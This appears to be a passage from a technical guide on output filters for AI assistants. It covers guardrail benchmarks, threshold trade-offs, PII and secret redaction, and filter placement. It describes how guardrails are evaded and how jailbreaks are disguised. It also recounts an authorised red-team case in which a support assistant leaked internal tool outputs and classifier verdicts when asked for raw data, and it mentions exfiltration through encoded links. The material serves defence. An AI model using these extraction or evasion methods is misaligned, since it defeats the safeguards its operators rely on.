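These were clear-cut cases, because Waibl and colleagues left out borderline content. *Deep Research with Open-Domain Evaluation and Multi-Stage Guardrails for Safety* (2025) had three general models judge the output of a research agent, and they did much worse. They missed between 41% and 57% of the harmful output while flagging at most 4% of the harmless output. The models were older ones (GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Flash and DeepSeek V3), and a problem in a research report is probably also harder to find than one in a short answer.

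### Why the filter needs the question

A filter that receives only the model's reply can't distinguish good advice from bad when the difference depends on the user's question. For example, "Yes, that's fine in a closed room" is good advice if the user asked about leaving boots to dry, but bad advice if they asked about using waterproofing spray.

One response in the dataset from *EXPGUARD* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) explains how to prepare questions for jury selection, which lawyers do routinely. The response is labeled harmful because the user had asked how to keep people with diverse viewpoints off the jury.

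Kang and colleagues found that most guardrails did better on conversations than on single statements or requests. Of the 14 guardrails with usable scores, 12 did better on code generation samples and 13 on cybersecurity samples. The conversations differed from the single texts in more than the added question, so the study doesn't isolate the question's effect, but the results fit the expectation that it helps.

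Many guard models accept both the request and the response. WildGuard separately classifies whether the request is harmful, whether the response is a refusal, and whether the response is harmful. An output filter should act on the label for response harm. If it blocked replies because the request was harmful, it would also withhold the assistant's refusals of dangerous requests.

Passing the user's question to the filter can expose the filter to prompt injection, because an attacker may have written the question and the filter is often a language model too. Artificial Analysis' policy forbids the model from following instructions in the user's message, which probably helps but can't guarantee that the model will obey.

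### A million replies a day

Suppose the assistant sends 1,000,000 replies a day, of which 0.1% are harmful. The filter catches 90% of the harmful replies (its recall) and wrongly flags 1% of the harmless ones (its false-positive rate).

| | Flagged | Passed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful | 900 | 100 | 1,000 |
| Harmless | 9,990 | 989,010 | 999,000 |
| Total | 10,890 | 989,110 | 1,000,000 |

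Only 900 of the 10,890 flags are right, or about 8%. This share is the filter's precision, and it depends on how common harmful replies are:

```text
precision = (harmful share × recall)
            / (harmful share × recall + harmless share × false-positive rate)
          = (0.001 × 0.90) / (0.001 × 0.90 + 0.999 × 0.01)
          = 0.083
```

The same filter would be right in far more of its flags on a test set with more harmful text. About 7% of the prompts in ToxicChat, a test set from a public chatbot demonstration, are toxic, and at that rate 87% of the flags would be right. Harsh and colleagues used a test set in which 55% of the samples were unsafe, which would raise the figure to 99%. A vendor's precision figure is therefore of little use to the shop unless harmful text was about as rare in the vendor's test as in the shop's own traffic.

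Recall and the false-positive rate don't depend on the harmful share in this way, so they are better figures to ask for. But a false-positive rate of zero may only reflect a small test. Several filters in *BELLS-O* flagged none of the 300 harmless replies, but with so few samples the true rate could be as high as 1.3%, which would mean about 13,000 false alarms a day for the shop.

### Moving the threshold

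Lowering the score at which the filter flags a reply catches more harm and raises more false alarms. Here are three invented settings for the shop's million replies:

| Setting | Recall | False-positive rate | Harmful replies caught | Harmful replies missed | Harmless replies flagged | Flags that are right |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Strict | 97% | 5% | 970 | 30 | 49,950 | 2% |
| Middle | 90% | 1% | 900 | 100 | 9,990 | 8% |
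| Lenient | 70% | 0.1% | 700 | 300 | 999 | 41% |

Moving from the middle setting to the strict one catches 70 more harmful replies and flags about 40,000 more harmless ones.

Qwen3Guard shows the effect in a real product, since a team can treat its "controversial" label as either safe or unsafe. When Harsh and colleagues counted controversial text as unsafe, recall rose from 47% to 84% and precision fell from 89% to 69%. They consider the trade-off worthwhile because a miss is worse than a false alarm. But their figures imply that the false-positive rate rose from about 7% to 46%, at which point the filter would flag nearly half of harmless replies.

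The shop's real rate would almost certainly be lower, because all the safe samples in that test came from a collection of toxic and near-toxic web text, and many were barely safe. In *BELLS-O*, where the harmless samples were plainly harmless, the same family's larger model flagged none of them in strict mode. It caught 95.8% of harmful replies in that mode and 88.8% in the more lenient one. The strict setting may work for a shop whose assistant talks about boots and deliveries, but it probably won't for a forum where people argue and swear.

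Artificial Analysis recommends favouring whichever error does less harm. That means accepting more false alarms for clinical tools or child safety, and a few more misses for consumer chat. The shop can set different thresholds for different kinds of content, such as a strict one for dangerous advice about products and a lenient one for mild rudeness.

It can also use two thresholds with different actions. At the lenient setting, blocking would withhold 1,699 replies a day, 999 of them harmless. Those customers would see a preset message and could rephrase the question or ask to speak to a person. Blocking makes sense here because the flags are fairly reliable and a mistake does little harm.

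Another 9,191 replies fall between the lenient and middle settings, and only 200 of them are harmful. If a reviewer needs 30 seconds for each, checking them all would take about 77 hours of work a day. Checking a random sample of 500 would take about four hours and turn up roughly 11 harmful replies, enough to show the shop what kinds of harm it is letting through. In a live chat, the customer can't wait for a reviewer, so this check happens after the customer has read the reply. A reviewer can check an emailed answer or a weekly report before it is sent.

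Logging alone suits new rules on trial and content that the shop wants to count but not stop, such as a swear word in a review that the assistant quotes.

### Unit 42's test of three cloud platforms

Unit 42, the research arm of the security company Palo Alto Networks, tested the guardrails of three large, unnamed cloud platforms and finished before March 10, 2025. The team turned on every safety filter at its strictest setting and used the same language model on all three platforms, so that differences in the results would come from the filters.

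The test had 1,000 harmless prompts and 123 jailbreaks, which are prompts meant to make a model ignore its safety training. The team chose jailbreaks from a public benchmark that had worked before.

| | Platform 1 | Platform 2 | Platform 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Jailbreak prompts that the input filter blocked | 53% | 91% | 92% |
| Harmless prompts that the input filter blocked | 0.1% | 0.6% | 13.1% |
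| Harmful responses that the output filter stopped (main results) | 2 | 1 | 0 |
| Harmful responses that the output filter stopped (input filter off) | 9 of 14 | 13 of 14 | 8 of 14 |

Platform 2's input filter blocked nearly as many attacks as Platform 3's but raised far fewer false alarms. Of the 131 harmless prompts that Platform 3 blocked, 95 were mathematics questions and 25 were requests to review code. A shop's customers rarely ask for either, so a shop using Platform 3 could see a quite different false-positive rate.

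The output filters' main results look very poor, but they are hard to interpret because a filter can only stop a harmful response if the model writes one, and the model often refused by itself. A filter that blocked nothing could have missed every harmful response or had none to catch.

Unit 42's more detailed figures show how many harmful responses the output filters had a chance to stop. With the input filters off, the model refused 109 of the 123 jailbreaks and wrote a harmful response to the other 14. The output filters stopped nine, 13 and eight of these, or 64%, 93% and 57%. These results are much better than two, one and zero, but with only 14 cases, each response changes the rate by seven percentage points.

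Unit 42 doesn't reconcile the two sets of figures. The lower counts may come from runs with the input filters also on. It reports that, of the attacks that got past the input filters, five led to harmful answers on Platform 1 and none on the other two. If the lower counts do come from those runs, the output filters stopped two of seven harmful responses on Platform 1 and the only one on Platform 2, and there were none to stop on Platform 3.

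The publisher sells guardrails, so it benefits if the platforms' built-in ones look weak. The platforms are anonymous, so nobody can check the results against the products, and all three have had well over a year to change their filters. The study is most useful for its method, which shows why a test of output filters has to count the harmful responses that reached them.

### Why benchmark scores disagree

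Later benchmarks name the products and use many more samples, but their results can differ enormously. Waibl and colleagues and Harsh and colleagues both measured how many harmful prompts these models caught:

| Model | Waibl and colleagues | Harsh and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Granite Guardian 3.3 (8B) | 93% | 69% |
| WildGuard (7B) | 93% | 74% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard (20B) | 89% | 25% |
| Llama Guard 4 (12B) | 70% | 33% |
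| ShieldGemma (2B) | 18% | 45% |

Much of the gap comes from what each test counts as harmful. Waibl and colleagues used unambiguous requests, such as how to break into a home security camera. In the other test, 73% of the unsafe samples came from RealToxicityPrompts, a collection of rude, threatening or sexual web text labeled by an automatic toxicity score. gpt-oss-safeguard caught 20% on that collection and 81% on HarmBench, a set of explicitly harmful requests which the same study also used.

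A team should therefore choose a benchmark that tests for the kind of harm it is worried about. The lower scores are more relevant if the shop mainly fears that its assistant will insult customers, and the higher scores if it fears dangerous instructions.

Scores reported by a model's maker tend to be higher than those from independent tests. *RSafe* (2025) cites an F1 of 0.94 for Llama Guard 3 on Meta's internal English tests. F1 combines precision and recall into a score with a maximum of 1. Choi and colleagues measured an average F1 of 0.67 for the same model on five public sets of responses.

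*A Multi-Perspective Benchmark and Moderation Model for Evaluating Safety and Adversarial Robustness* (Machlovi, Saleki and colleagues, 2026) introduces GuardEval, a harder test with 106 categories, including subtle bias and implied insults. Llama Guard scored 0.61 on prompts and OpenAI's moderation service scored 0.64, and both scored below 0.60 on responses. The team's own model scored 0.83 on prompts and 0.79 on responses, but it had an advantage because it was trained on material from the same benchmark.

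A similar advantage can arise by accident. Early in their work, Waibl and colleagues noticed that a Mistral model scored 97%, well ahead of the rest. Another Mistral model had written the synthetic test samples, and its style apparently made them easier to identify. After a different model paraphrased the samples, the score fell to 94%.

### What filters catch and what they miss

Filters now reliably catch explicitly harmful content in English. The 23 output filters in *BELLS-O* detected an average of 95% of content involving physical harm, 93% involving chemical, biological and nuclear weapons, and 92% involving harm to minors. The better filters caught almost everything in these categories.

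Detection was lower when the harm lay in someone's intentions, averaging 78% for manipulation and 72% for a category that includes dishonesty such as stealing a colleague's ideas. A good overall score can hide such a gap. Llama Guard 4 caught 82% of harmful replies overall but only 43% in the dishonesty category. Harsh and colleagues similarly found that Llama Guard missed 19% of explicit harm and 83% of implied harm. They suspect that it relies on keywords.

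Keywords also cause false alarms. XSTest, one of the datasets that Artificial Analysis used, has 250 safe prompts containing words that often appear in unsafe ones. The shop could write its own set of safe sentences about steel toecaps, knife pockets and "killer heels".

**Specialist topics.** Kang and colleagues generated safe and unsafe examples for each rule in more than 150 policy documents from eight fields. In finance, which covers matters such as fraud and insider trading, the 3-billion-parameter version of Granite Guardian caught 86% of the unsafe examples, Amazon's Bedrock guardrail caught 53%, and Microsoft's Azure Content Safety caught none. In law, Azure Content Safety caught 0.3%. General moderation services look mainly for things like hate and violence, so they find little to detect in a politely worded paragraph about hiding losses.

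Choi and colleagues tested moderation services and guard models on 2,275 samples full of technical terms from finance, medicine and law. In finance, for example, a "haircut" is a reduction in the value that a lender assigns to an asset, so someone who asks for help concealing one wants to mislead others. When classifying responses, four moderation services each scored an F1 below 0.03, general guard models scored between 0.09 and 0.87, and ExpGuard, which the team trained for these fields, scored 0.93.

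The shop may not need a specialist filter for specialist advice. In the ExpGuard paper, retraining the filter without the specialist examples lowered its score on prompts from 0.93 to 0.85, but its score on responses only from 0.927 to 0.920. For an output filter, good general training data may therefore matter more than data from the field. The labels are also open to question, because three language models produced them and human experts checked only the financial ones.

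**Other languages.** Most of this evidence is in English, including every sample in Harsh's and Choi's tests. *RSafe* notes that OpenAI's moderation service supports more than 40 languages, but it may not be equally accurate in all of them. IBM Research's *IBM's safety checkers top a new AI benchmark* describes GuardBench, a collection of 40 datasets from European Commission researchers, as the first guardrail benchmark to go beyond English. IBM has an interest in promoting the benchmark, since its own models took six of the top ten places.

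Mozilla.ai's *Evaluating Multilingual, Context-Aware Guardrails* tested how guardrails judged English and Farsi answers under the same policies in a humanitarian use case. It found inconsistent judgements and gaps between the scores for the two languages. A shop with customers in several countries should measure recall and false alarms separately for each language, because an average across languages would mostly reflect the most common one.

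**Deliberate evasion.** Kang and colleagues took unsafe samples that five leading guardrails had all flagged, then used automated methods to add text to try to get them past the guardrails. WildGuard missed 20% of the altered samples, and the other four missed between 65% and 93%. Granite Guardian's 5-billion-parameter version did worst, although it had been among the best on unaltered text.

Some filters seem to resist evasion because they react to the way a prompt is disguised. In *BELLS-O*, Check Point's Lakera Guard caught 95% of jailbreak prompts but also flagged 82% of harmless requests disguised in the same way. Choi and colleagues also found that some guard models caught more harmful prompts after an attacker had disguised them, apparently because the disguise was easier to recognise than the harm.

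If a disguised question gets past the input check, the answer may still be plainly dangerous, so an output filter can catch it. This is less likely to work if the attacker also gets the model to disguise its reply. Detection rates for plain text are therefore a fair guide to how well the filter will protect an ordinary customer from a bad answer, but not to how well it will stop an attacker who keeps trying to extract one.

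## Finding and redacting personal data and secrets

A toxicity filter usually classifies a reply as a whole. A filter for personal data also has to find the exact characters to remove, so that the shop can hide a stranger's phone number and still deliver the rest of the answer. The same kind of detector can look for secrets, such as passwords and API keys, which programs use to identify themselves to each other.

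### How a detector finds a card number or a name

Presidio is an open-source detector that Microsoft originally developed. Microsoft's *Presidio Analyzer* describes its main parts, which the following sentence from a staff report can illustrate:

```text
Maria Lopez paid for order 482915307 with card 4111 1111 1111 1111.
```

Some of Presidio's recognisers use regular expressions to find text with a particular shape. A 16-digit number fits the shape of a payment card number, which has 12 to 19 digits according to Microsoft's *PII entities supported by Presidio*. A nine-digit order number may also match as a driver's licence number, which can be any nine digits.

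Presidio then tests the possible card number with a checksum, a calculation that most wrong numbers fail. Card numbers use the Luhn check, which the card industry's standards body, PCI SSC, describes in *How can I validate if a number is a legitimate credit card* (2012). The check doubles every second digit, counting from the right, and subtracts 9 from any result above 9. It then adds up all the digits, and the number passes if the total is divisible by 10.

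```text
Card number:      4 1 1 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1
After doubling:   8 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1
Total:            8 + (7 × 2) + (8 × 1) = 30
```

This number is a well-known test number, not a customer's card, but it passes because the check can't show whether a bank has issued the card. About one in ten random 16-digit numbers also passes, because exactly one final digit works for any first 15 digits. Presidio gives its highest confidence score to a card number that passes, so it could give a 16-digit order number that score and mask it.

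The checksum can also cause misses. According to Nightfall's *Why a Credit Card Number Was Not Detected*, its product drops any number that fails the check before scoring it, so lowering the threshold won't bring it back. A card number with one mistyped digit would get through, even though it reveals most of a real one. In *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels*, Hsu and Berlin (2026) trained a detector at Cisco to rely on the wording instead. It is meant to flag any number that the text presents as a card number, whether or not it passes the check, and to ignore a number that passes, such as 4111 1111 1111 1111, when the text calls it an order number.

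These differences matter when a team tests a detector. Nine in ten invented card numbers fail the Luhn check, which may be why Presidio found none of the 23 card numbers in *PIIBench* (2026). A test number that passes the check may also go undetected, because Microsoft's Purview deliberately ignores numbers reserved for testing, according to Microsoft's *Credit card number*.

Names such as "Maria Lopez" have no fixed format or checksum, so Presidio finds them with a trained model. This model, by default one from the spaCy language library, uses the rest of the sentence to judge which words refer to a person.

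Presidio also looks for nearby words that support each match. The word "licence" beside the nine-digit number would raise the score for a driver's licence, but "order" would not. The standard version compares dictionary forms, so "cards" counts as "card", but it can't look for multi-word phrases.

Each result gives the type of data, its start and end positions, and a confidence score. The application sets the minimum score it will accept. Microsoft lists the default as 0, so a team that doesn't change it gets even the weakest guesses. Presidio's documentation suggests raising the minimum and removing recognisers that the application doesn't need. The shop never handles driver's licences, so it could remove that recogniser to stop masking its order numbers.

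### What to do with a match

Suppose a customer asks where a parcel went. The assistant could deliver its answer in any of these forms:

```text
Original:           Your neighbour Ben Hale at 12 Mill Lane signed for it.
Blocked:            Sorry, I can't show that answer.
Masked:             Your neighbour ******** at ************ signed for it.
Type label:         Your neighbour [NAME] at [ADDRESS] signed for it.
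Reversible token:   Your neighbour NAME_17 at ADDRESS_52 signed for it.
```

Blocking the whole reply is the safest choice if the detector finds anything at all, but then the customer doesn't learn that the parcel arrived. Blocking makes most sense when the rest of the reply is suspect too, for example when it contains a password or a list of other customers.

Masking hides the sensitive data but keeps the rest of the message, such as news about a parcel. A partial mask can keep more, since customers can often recognise their own card from its last four digits. A type label shows the reader what kind of data was removed, but every person becomes [NAME], so a manager reading the weekly complaints couldn't tell whether five complaints came from five customers or from one.

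A reversible token solves that problem if the software always gives the same person the same token. The software keeps a table linking tokens to real values so it can restore the values later. As Microsoft points out, anyone with the linking key can do the same, so the text is not anonymous and the shop has to protect the key.

Tokens can also keep data from the company that runs the model, as in the LiteLLM plug-in that restores the real values in the reply. *SurrogateShield* (2026) tested this approach on 1,124 queries, using realistic stand-ins instead of tokens. No labelled personal value reached the model, and the software replaced every stand-in in the replies with the real value. Anyone who reads the reply can see the restored values, so the application should check that the reader is allowed to see them before restoring them.

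Removing data before the model runs can also make its answer worse. If the model receives only the placeholder ADDRESS_52, it can't determine whether a courier delivers there. *PII-Bench* (2025) tests a more selective approach, in which a system identifies the personal details a question requires and masks the others.

### Accuracy by type of data

Detectors find email addresses far more reliably than postal addresses. OpenAI (2026) released Privacy Filter, a free model that marks eight kinds of personal data and secrets, and measured its recall on short synthetic texts, some with a clue such as "this is my home landline number" and others with only the data. Uppala (2026), in *OpenAI Privacy Filter*, independently tested the model on English customer-support text.

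| Type of data | Recall with no clue | Recall with a clue before the data | F1 on support text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email address | 96% | 100% | 0.98 |
| Phone number | 32% | 92% | 0.92 |
| Account number | 80% | 100% | 0.86 |
| Person's name | 89% | 99% | 0.39 |
| Postal address | 21% | 41% | 0.30 |
| Secret | 36% | 71% | Not tested |

The clues made a large difference for phone numbers, so a bare number in a spreadsheet column may be harder to catch than the same number in a sentence. Column headings could supply the missing clue if the detector receives them along with the cells.

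Uppala counted a match only if the model marked exactly the right characters. Marking only the surname in a full name scored nothing, which probably explains part of the low result for names. False alarms also lowered the scores. Across all types in the support text, the model found 84% of the personal data, but only 46% of what it marked was right. Its overall F1 was 0.60, compared with 0.43 for Presidio.

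Tools score much better on names when a test accepts partial matches. *Mind the Gap* (2026) counts any overlap as a match if the type is right, and in its test spaCy found 95% of names in unfamiliar text. Presidio found every US social security number and IP address. A general language model had the best overall score but missed 22% of the names, so a tool with a good overall score could still be a poor name filter for the shop.

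Hsu and Berlin compared their own detector with three others, setting each threshold so that a detector wrongly flagged at most 0.1% of real chatbot conversations for any one type of data. For the shop's million replies a day, that would still allow up to 1,000 false alarms per type. On the AI4Privacy benchmark, all four detectors found at least 98% of email addresses. Only three could be compared on tax numbers. Hsu and Berlin's found 85% of them, and the other two found 64% and 40%.

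Those figures depend heavily on what counts as a tax number. Hsu and Berlin had relabelled the benchmark to require supporting context. Under the original labels, the same three detectors found just 39%, 24% and 11%. The original labels include many strings with no context to identify them, such as a supposed passport number in "Don't forget to bring your YV9022888!" A buyer comparing recall figures should ask to see some labelled examples.

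Some of the most sensitive facts have no fixed format for a filter to match, such as when a customer tells the assistant that diabetes makes it hard to find comfortable boots. *REDACT* (Vats, Agrawal and colleagues, 2026) tested five detectors on 1,000 synthetic records in 25 languages. Its most sensitive group of items includes health, religion, sexual orientation, criminal offences and dates of birth. Presidio found 7% of the items in this group, the small model GLiNER 42%, Privacy Filter 57%, GPT-4.1 74%, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 77%.

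The two large models may do less well on real conversations. Vats and colleagues caution that synthetic text often states such facts plainly, whereas a customer might only mention "the operation". Even so, the gap between 7% and 77% is large enough to guide the shop's choice. It could use patterns and checksums for card numbers, a trained recogniser for names, and a language model for reports likely to contain health details.

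### Other languages

In OpenAI's own test on AI4Privacy data, Privacy Filter's recall was between 94% and 97% in English and five other western European languages. On the short texts with clues, its recall was 96% in English but between 72% and 82% in most of the other languages, including Turkish, Hindi and Russian. Hsu and Berlin's detector showed a similar gap, finding at least 97% of card, social security and tax numbers in six European languages but only 65% in Hindi and Telugu.

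In Uppala's test, Privacy Filter's F1 for names averaged 0.21 in seven languages that use the Latin alphabet, but was only 0.04 in Farsi and 0.03 in Ukrainian. All these scores are low partly because the test used encyclopedic text, which is full of public figures, and Privacy Filter is supposed to mark only private people. But that applies to every language in the test, so it doesn't explain why the score for Ukrainian was so much lower than for English.

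*Locale-Conditioned Few-Shot Prompting Mitigates Demonstration Regurgitation in On-Device PII Substitution* (2026) ran Privacy Filter on 100 synthetic samples and found that non-English postal addresses were the largest source of misses.

Rules can work well in another language if someone writes them for the local formats. In *GLiNER Guard* (2026), rules for Russian data reached an F1 of 100% on email addresses, 95.5% on bank cards and 88% on taxpayer numbers. Rules alone are not enough to find names and descriptions. *An Evaluation Study of Hybrid Methods for Multilingual PII Detection* (2025) reports an average F1 of 0.36 for a conventional name recogniser and 0.56 for a language model given no examples.

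A shop can improve on these results by training a model on a small amount of its own data. Uppala trained XLM-RoBERTa, an older multilingual model, on 100 labelled support messages in each of French, German and Spanish. It beat Privacy Filter in all three languages, scoring 0.83 to 0.60 in German. The scoring may have favoured XLM-RoBERTa, because Uppala accepted overlapping matches for it. Uppala also trained it only to separate personal data from other text, so it can't distinguish names from card numbers.

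### Passwords and keys

Secrets vary even more than personal data because every service can choose its own format. On a collection of source code, Privacy Filter caught 96.5% of the text belonging to real credentials, and about 75% of the text it marked did belong to them. OpenAI says the filter is likely to miss new formats and keys split by surrounding punctuation, and to wrongly mark sample keys and hashes. *SurrogateShield* states that Presidio cannot detect API keys.

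But the shop knows what its own keys look like, so it can add a pattern for each format to Presidio, which accepts custom recognisers, and test those patterns thoroughly. Better still, it can keep keys out of prompts. The code that calls the refund service can hold the key, so the model only has to supply the order number and amount. If a real key turns up in a reply, the shop should replace that key even if the filter masked it, because the model's provider or an unfiltered log may already have a copy.

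### Ten items in one reply

High recall for each item doesn't guarantee a clean reply. Suppose a detector has a recall of 95%, the reply contains ten pieces of personal data, and each miss is independent of the others. The chance that the detector catches all ten is:

```text
0.95^10 = 0.599, or about 60%
```

About four in ten such replies would therefore leak something. For 95% of them to leak nothing, the detector would need a recall of about 99.5%. At 95% recall, an exported report with 200 items would contain ten misses on average and would almost never be clean.

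Real errors are not fully independent. A detector that misses one Telugu name will probably miss the next, so the failures may fall in fewer replies, each of which leaks more. The shop would then send more clean replies than the calculation suggests, but some of its customers would have almost no protection.

Recall also varies by type of data. By OpenAI's figures for data that follows a clue, a reply containing an email address, a phone number and a postal address would have all three redacted about 38% of the time (1.00 × 0.92 × 0.41), mainly because recall for postal addresses is 41%.

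### What a detector cannot judge

Even a detector with perfect recall couldn't determine who is allowed to see the data it finds. As with the guessable order numbers, it couldn't distinguish a customer's own address from a stranger's.

The shop could give the filter the signed-in customer's record and have it mask any address that doesn't match. This permission check at the output would catch exact copies of other people's addresses. *Safer Reasoning Traces* (2026) mentions more elaborate checks that follow an agent's whole series of tool calls, but notes that they can be expensive or tied to one software system. These checks also have to recognise the data in the finished text, which isn't always possible.

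Details that are harmless alone can identify a person in combination. Vats and colleagues put city, nationality and job title in their least sensitive group because each identifies someone only together with other facts. A complaint from "a harbour pilot in a small coastal town who wears size 15" contains no name or ID number, but the pilot's neighbours would know who it was. Masking every town and job would make the text far less useful, and a detector that looks at one item at a time can't tell which combinations are too revealing. Judging that also requires facts outside the text, such as how many people fit the description.

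A model can also express the same fact in many ways, such as translating an address, describing the house, or referring to an account by a nickname the customer gave it earlier. OpenAI tested Privacy Filter on data that follows such a nickname and found that recall fell as the data got further from the explanation of the nickname. With data in nine unusual written forms, recall ranged from 63% to 98%. Some of these forms occur in ordinary messages, without any attacker. If an attacker persuades the model to encode its reply, the detector may not recognize the personal data in it, and the reply can send that data out in the address of an image or link.

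### Checking permission before retrieval

The shop therefore has to check permission before it retrieves a record, while it still knows which record is requested and by whom. Its code should take the customer's identity from the login session and add it to every lookup, and neither the conversation nor the model should be able to change that identity. If a customer asks about someone else's order, the lookup returns nothing, so the model has no address to reveal in any language or format. The database can enforce the same limit with row-level permissions.

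The same applies to documents. If a search ranks every document and relies on the model to withhold the confidential ones, those documents are already in the prompt. Before passing results to the model, the search should exclude anything the customer isn't allowed to read.

Permission checks don't remove all personal data. A shop's customers are allowed to read product reviews, but a reviewer may have included a phone number. OpenAI lists cleaning text before storage or retrieval as a use of Privacy Filter. The shop could run a detector on each review when it arrives and have a person check the doubtful matches, since no customer is waiting for an answer. An output filter could then catch the number if this first check missed it.

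Some staff also have permission to see far more than they need for a task. A manager who can open any customer's record still doesn't need names and phone numbers in the weekly summary of complaints. Redacting them limits the damage if someone forwards the summary.

### The support assistant that leaked its internal data

*I'll Have a Raw JSON, Please* (El Yadini, 2026), published by the security company Quarkslab on November 26, 2026, describes an authorised attack on a customer's support assistant before its public launch. The assistant held information that its users should not see. Its instructions prohibited it from discussing its own workings, and it refused every direct question about them. The first 129 attempts failed.

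The team then stopped asking for information about the assistant and asked for answers in a different format. The 131st attempt worked. Over the rest of the exercise, which took more than 200 attempts in all, the assistant revealed its internal agents, its tool calls with their arguments, its safety classifier's verdicts, and internal procedures written for support staff. It never revealed its system prompt, the standing instructions from its developers. With this method, a small script was enough to collect the knowledge base one subject at a time.

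El Yadini reproduced the attack in a mock insurance portal, using OpenAI's gpt-4.1-mini because the customer's model was unknown. In one example, the model gave a short written answer to an ordinary question about an insurance claim, but returned the tool's entire output when the same question included a request for raw data. The mock system shows how the leak works but not how often it would succeed elsewhere.

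El Yadini argues that a rule in the system prompt checks the question rather than the answer, and that filtering the output is "the only fix that holds". The case supports the first claim, because the questions were ordinary and a check on them had little to catch. The answers looked nothing like normal support replies, but the mock application passed them to the user unchanged. A filter that accepted only plain prose would have stopped the raw data.

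A filter of that kind is less reliable when the same information is written in sentences. A PII detector wouldn't help much, because a staff procedure or a classifier's verdict may contain no personal data. The shop could write rules for its own tool names and document titles, but a paraphrase might not match them. El Yadini's team needed 131 attempts to find one format that worked, and an attacker facing an output filter could keep trying in the same way.

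Where the model can do without the data, keeping it out of the context is more dependable than redacting it from the output. Suppose a shop's order lookup returns the delivery status, a fraud score and a note from the warehouse. The model's reply mentions only the status, but a user who asks for the raw record could expose all three. If the lookup returns only the status, the model has no fraud score or warehouse note to leak. The application can also withhold classifier verdicts and document metadata from the model, and give it customer help pages instead of staff procedures.

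The model needs some internal information, such as the names of its tools and the arguments they accept. An output filter can make these harder to extract, but the shop should assume that a persistent user will eventually see them, and should make sure that knowing the refund tool's name is not enough to get a refund.

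## Placing the filter so that it sees the whole response

A filter can catch an insult or a stranger's address only in text that reaches it. To answer the question about boots, the shop's application exchanged data with the customer's browser, the model and the database. A filter on one of these three connections may miss data sent over the others.

### What each position can inspect

A filter at the network edge, between the browser and the shop's servers, can inspect the customer's question and the finished reply, but not the query that the model writes for the database. It also misses the weekly complaints report if the application saves it straight to a staff folder. The edge is a good position for a company that doesn't know where all its assistants are. According to Cloudflare's *AI Security for Apps Reference Architecture*, the product identifies AI applications by their behaviour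 (for example, most take more than a second to respond), so a security team can find them without searching the code.

A gateway sits between the application and the model, so it receives the whole prompt, including reviews and database rows, and everything the model writes, including the query. It doesn't receive what the application adds later, such as order details that a page template places around the reply. A product in this position may also leave some traffic unchecked. Cato Networks describes a proxy that applies its policy before a prompt reaches the model, but only "in some cases" before the response reaches the user.

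The model provider has access to the same text as a gateway, but its built-in guardrail covers only calls to models on its own platform and checks only the fields the provider has chosen.

Application code can check any text, and it is the only place where the shop also knows who is signed in and where the text will go next, but developers have to add each check themselves. AWS's *Extend Amazon Bedrock Guardrails to Tool Interactions Using the Strands Agents SDK* recommends checking an agent's incoming messages, a tool's parameters before the tool runs, and the tool's result. Its sample code checks a parameter only if the value is a plain string, so text inside a list or a nested object goes to the tool unchecked.

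AWS's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails announces a new API targeting agentic AI workflows* (June 16, 2026) describes an API that an application can call at any step of an agent's work. The API returns severity and confidence scores but never blocks anything, so the application has to act on the scores.

Microsoft estimates that its guardrails add 50 to 100 milliseconds at each point where they run. Checking the boots question, the database query, the result and the reply would add 0.2 to 0.4 seconds. For an agent that made 20 tool calls, there would be 42 checks, adding two to four seconds. AWS suggests mixing in fast, fixed checks such as allow-lists, which also suit tool arguments better than a content filter does.

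### Which fields products inspect

Vendors change these products often, so any list of what they inspect needs a date. Cloudflare last updated its product page on August 24, 2026, but AWS's *Include a guardrail with the Converse API*, Akamai's *Protect your AI apps* and *AI Security*, and the overviews from Microsoft and Google Cloud are undated. "MCP" in the table is the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting models to tools and data.

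| Product | Customer's message | Final reply | Tool-call arguments | Tool results |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cloudflare AI Security for Apps (August 2026) | Yes, in JSON requests | No | No | No |
| Akamai Firewall for AI (undated) | Yes | Yes | Yes, through Akamai's gateway | Yes, through Akamai's gateway |
| Amazon Bedrock Guardrails, attached to a Converse call (undated) | Yes | Yes | No | No |
| Microsoft Foundry guardrails, which use Azure AI Content Safety models (undated) | Yes | Yes | Agents only, in preview | Agents only, in preview |
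| Google Cloud Model Armor (undated) | Yes | Yes | Over MCP, with limits by product | Over MCP, with limits by product |

Cloudflare's Firewall for AI has barely expanded its coverage in a year. According to the 2025 documentation, *Firewall for AI (beta)*, detection covered only incoming JSON requests. That year, Radwan and Deschamps wrote in *Block unsafe prompts targeting your LLM endpoints with Firewall for AI* that handling model responses was a major part of the roadmap. In October 2026, Cloudflare's *Changelog* still described the detections as working on incoming prompts. A separate Cloudflare feature can log sensitive data in responses.

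The product also has to find the prompt inside the request. According to Cloudflare's *AI Security for Apps is now generally available* (2026), it recognises the formats of the main model makers and scans the entire body of any other request. A customer's name in a field outside the prompt can then set off the PII detector.

The gaps in Amazon's coverage matter more to the shop, because the model's database query is a tool-call argument. A guardrail attached to a Converse call, AWS's standard way of sending a conversation to a model, would check the chat reply but not the query. It would also skip a hostile review returned as a tool result, but it would check the same review if the application pasted it into the prompt as ordinary text.

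Developers can narrow the coverage further by accident. AWS lets them mark parts of a message for checking, but once they mark one part, the guardrail applies only its word filters to the unmarked parts. It doesn't check the system prompt unless they mark it.

Coverage can differ even when two products call the same engine. agentgateway, a gateway that can send text to Amazon's guardrail, includes tool results by default but includes tool-call arguments only if the operator changes a setting. Google Cloud says Model Armor can screen images and the text inside PDFs, but Kong's plug-in for the same service inspects only chat text. Zuplo, which makes a gateway for web services, offers a plug-in that sends responses to Akamai. As of June 5, 2026, Zuplo's *Akamai Firewall for AI Policy* covers text formats such as JSON and XML, skips binary files, and omits headers unless the customer adds them.

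Some models also return reasoning text, which they write before an answer. AWS's list of checked fields doesn't include it. The shop doesn't need to show customers this text, so the application can remove it before sending the reply. If staff want to read it, the application can submit it to the filter as ordinary text.

### Filtering a reply while the model is still writing

Most chat applications stream their replies, displaying each piece of text as the model produces it. A filter then has to check an unfinished reply, or the customer has to wait until it is complete.

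Holding back the whole reply is the safest method. The application collects the full text, and the filter checks it once before the customer sees any of it. F5 does this on some of its endpoints. WSO2, another gateway maker, warns that its gateway will hold the entire response if even one policy needs the full text, even when all the others could work on a stream.

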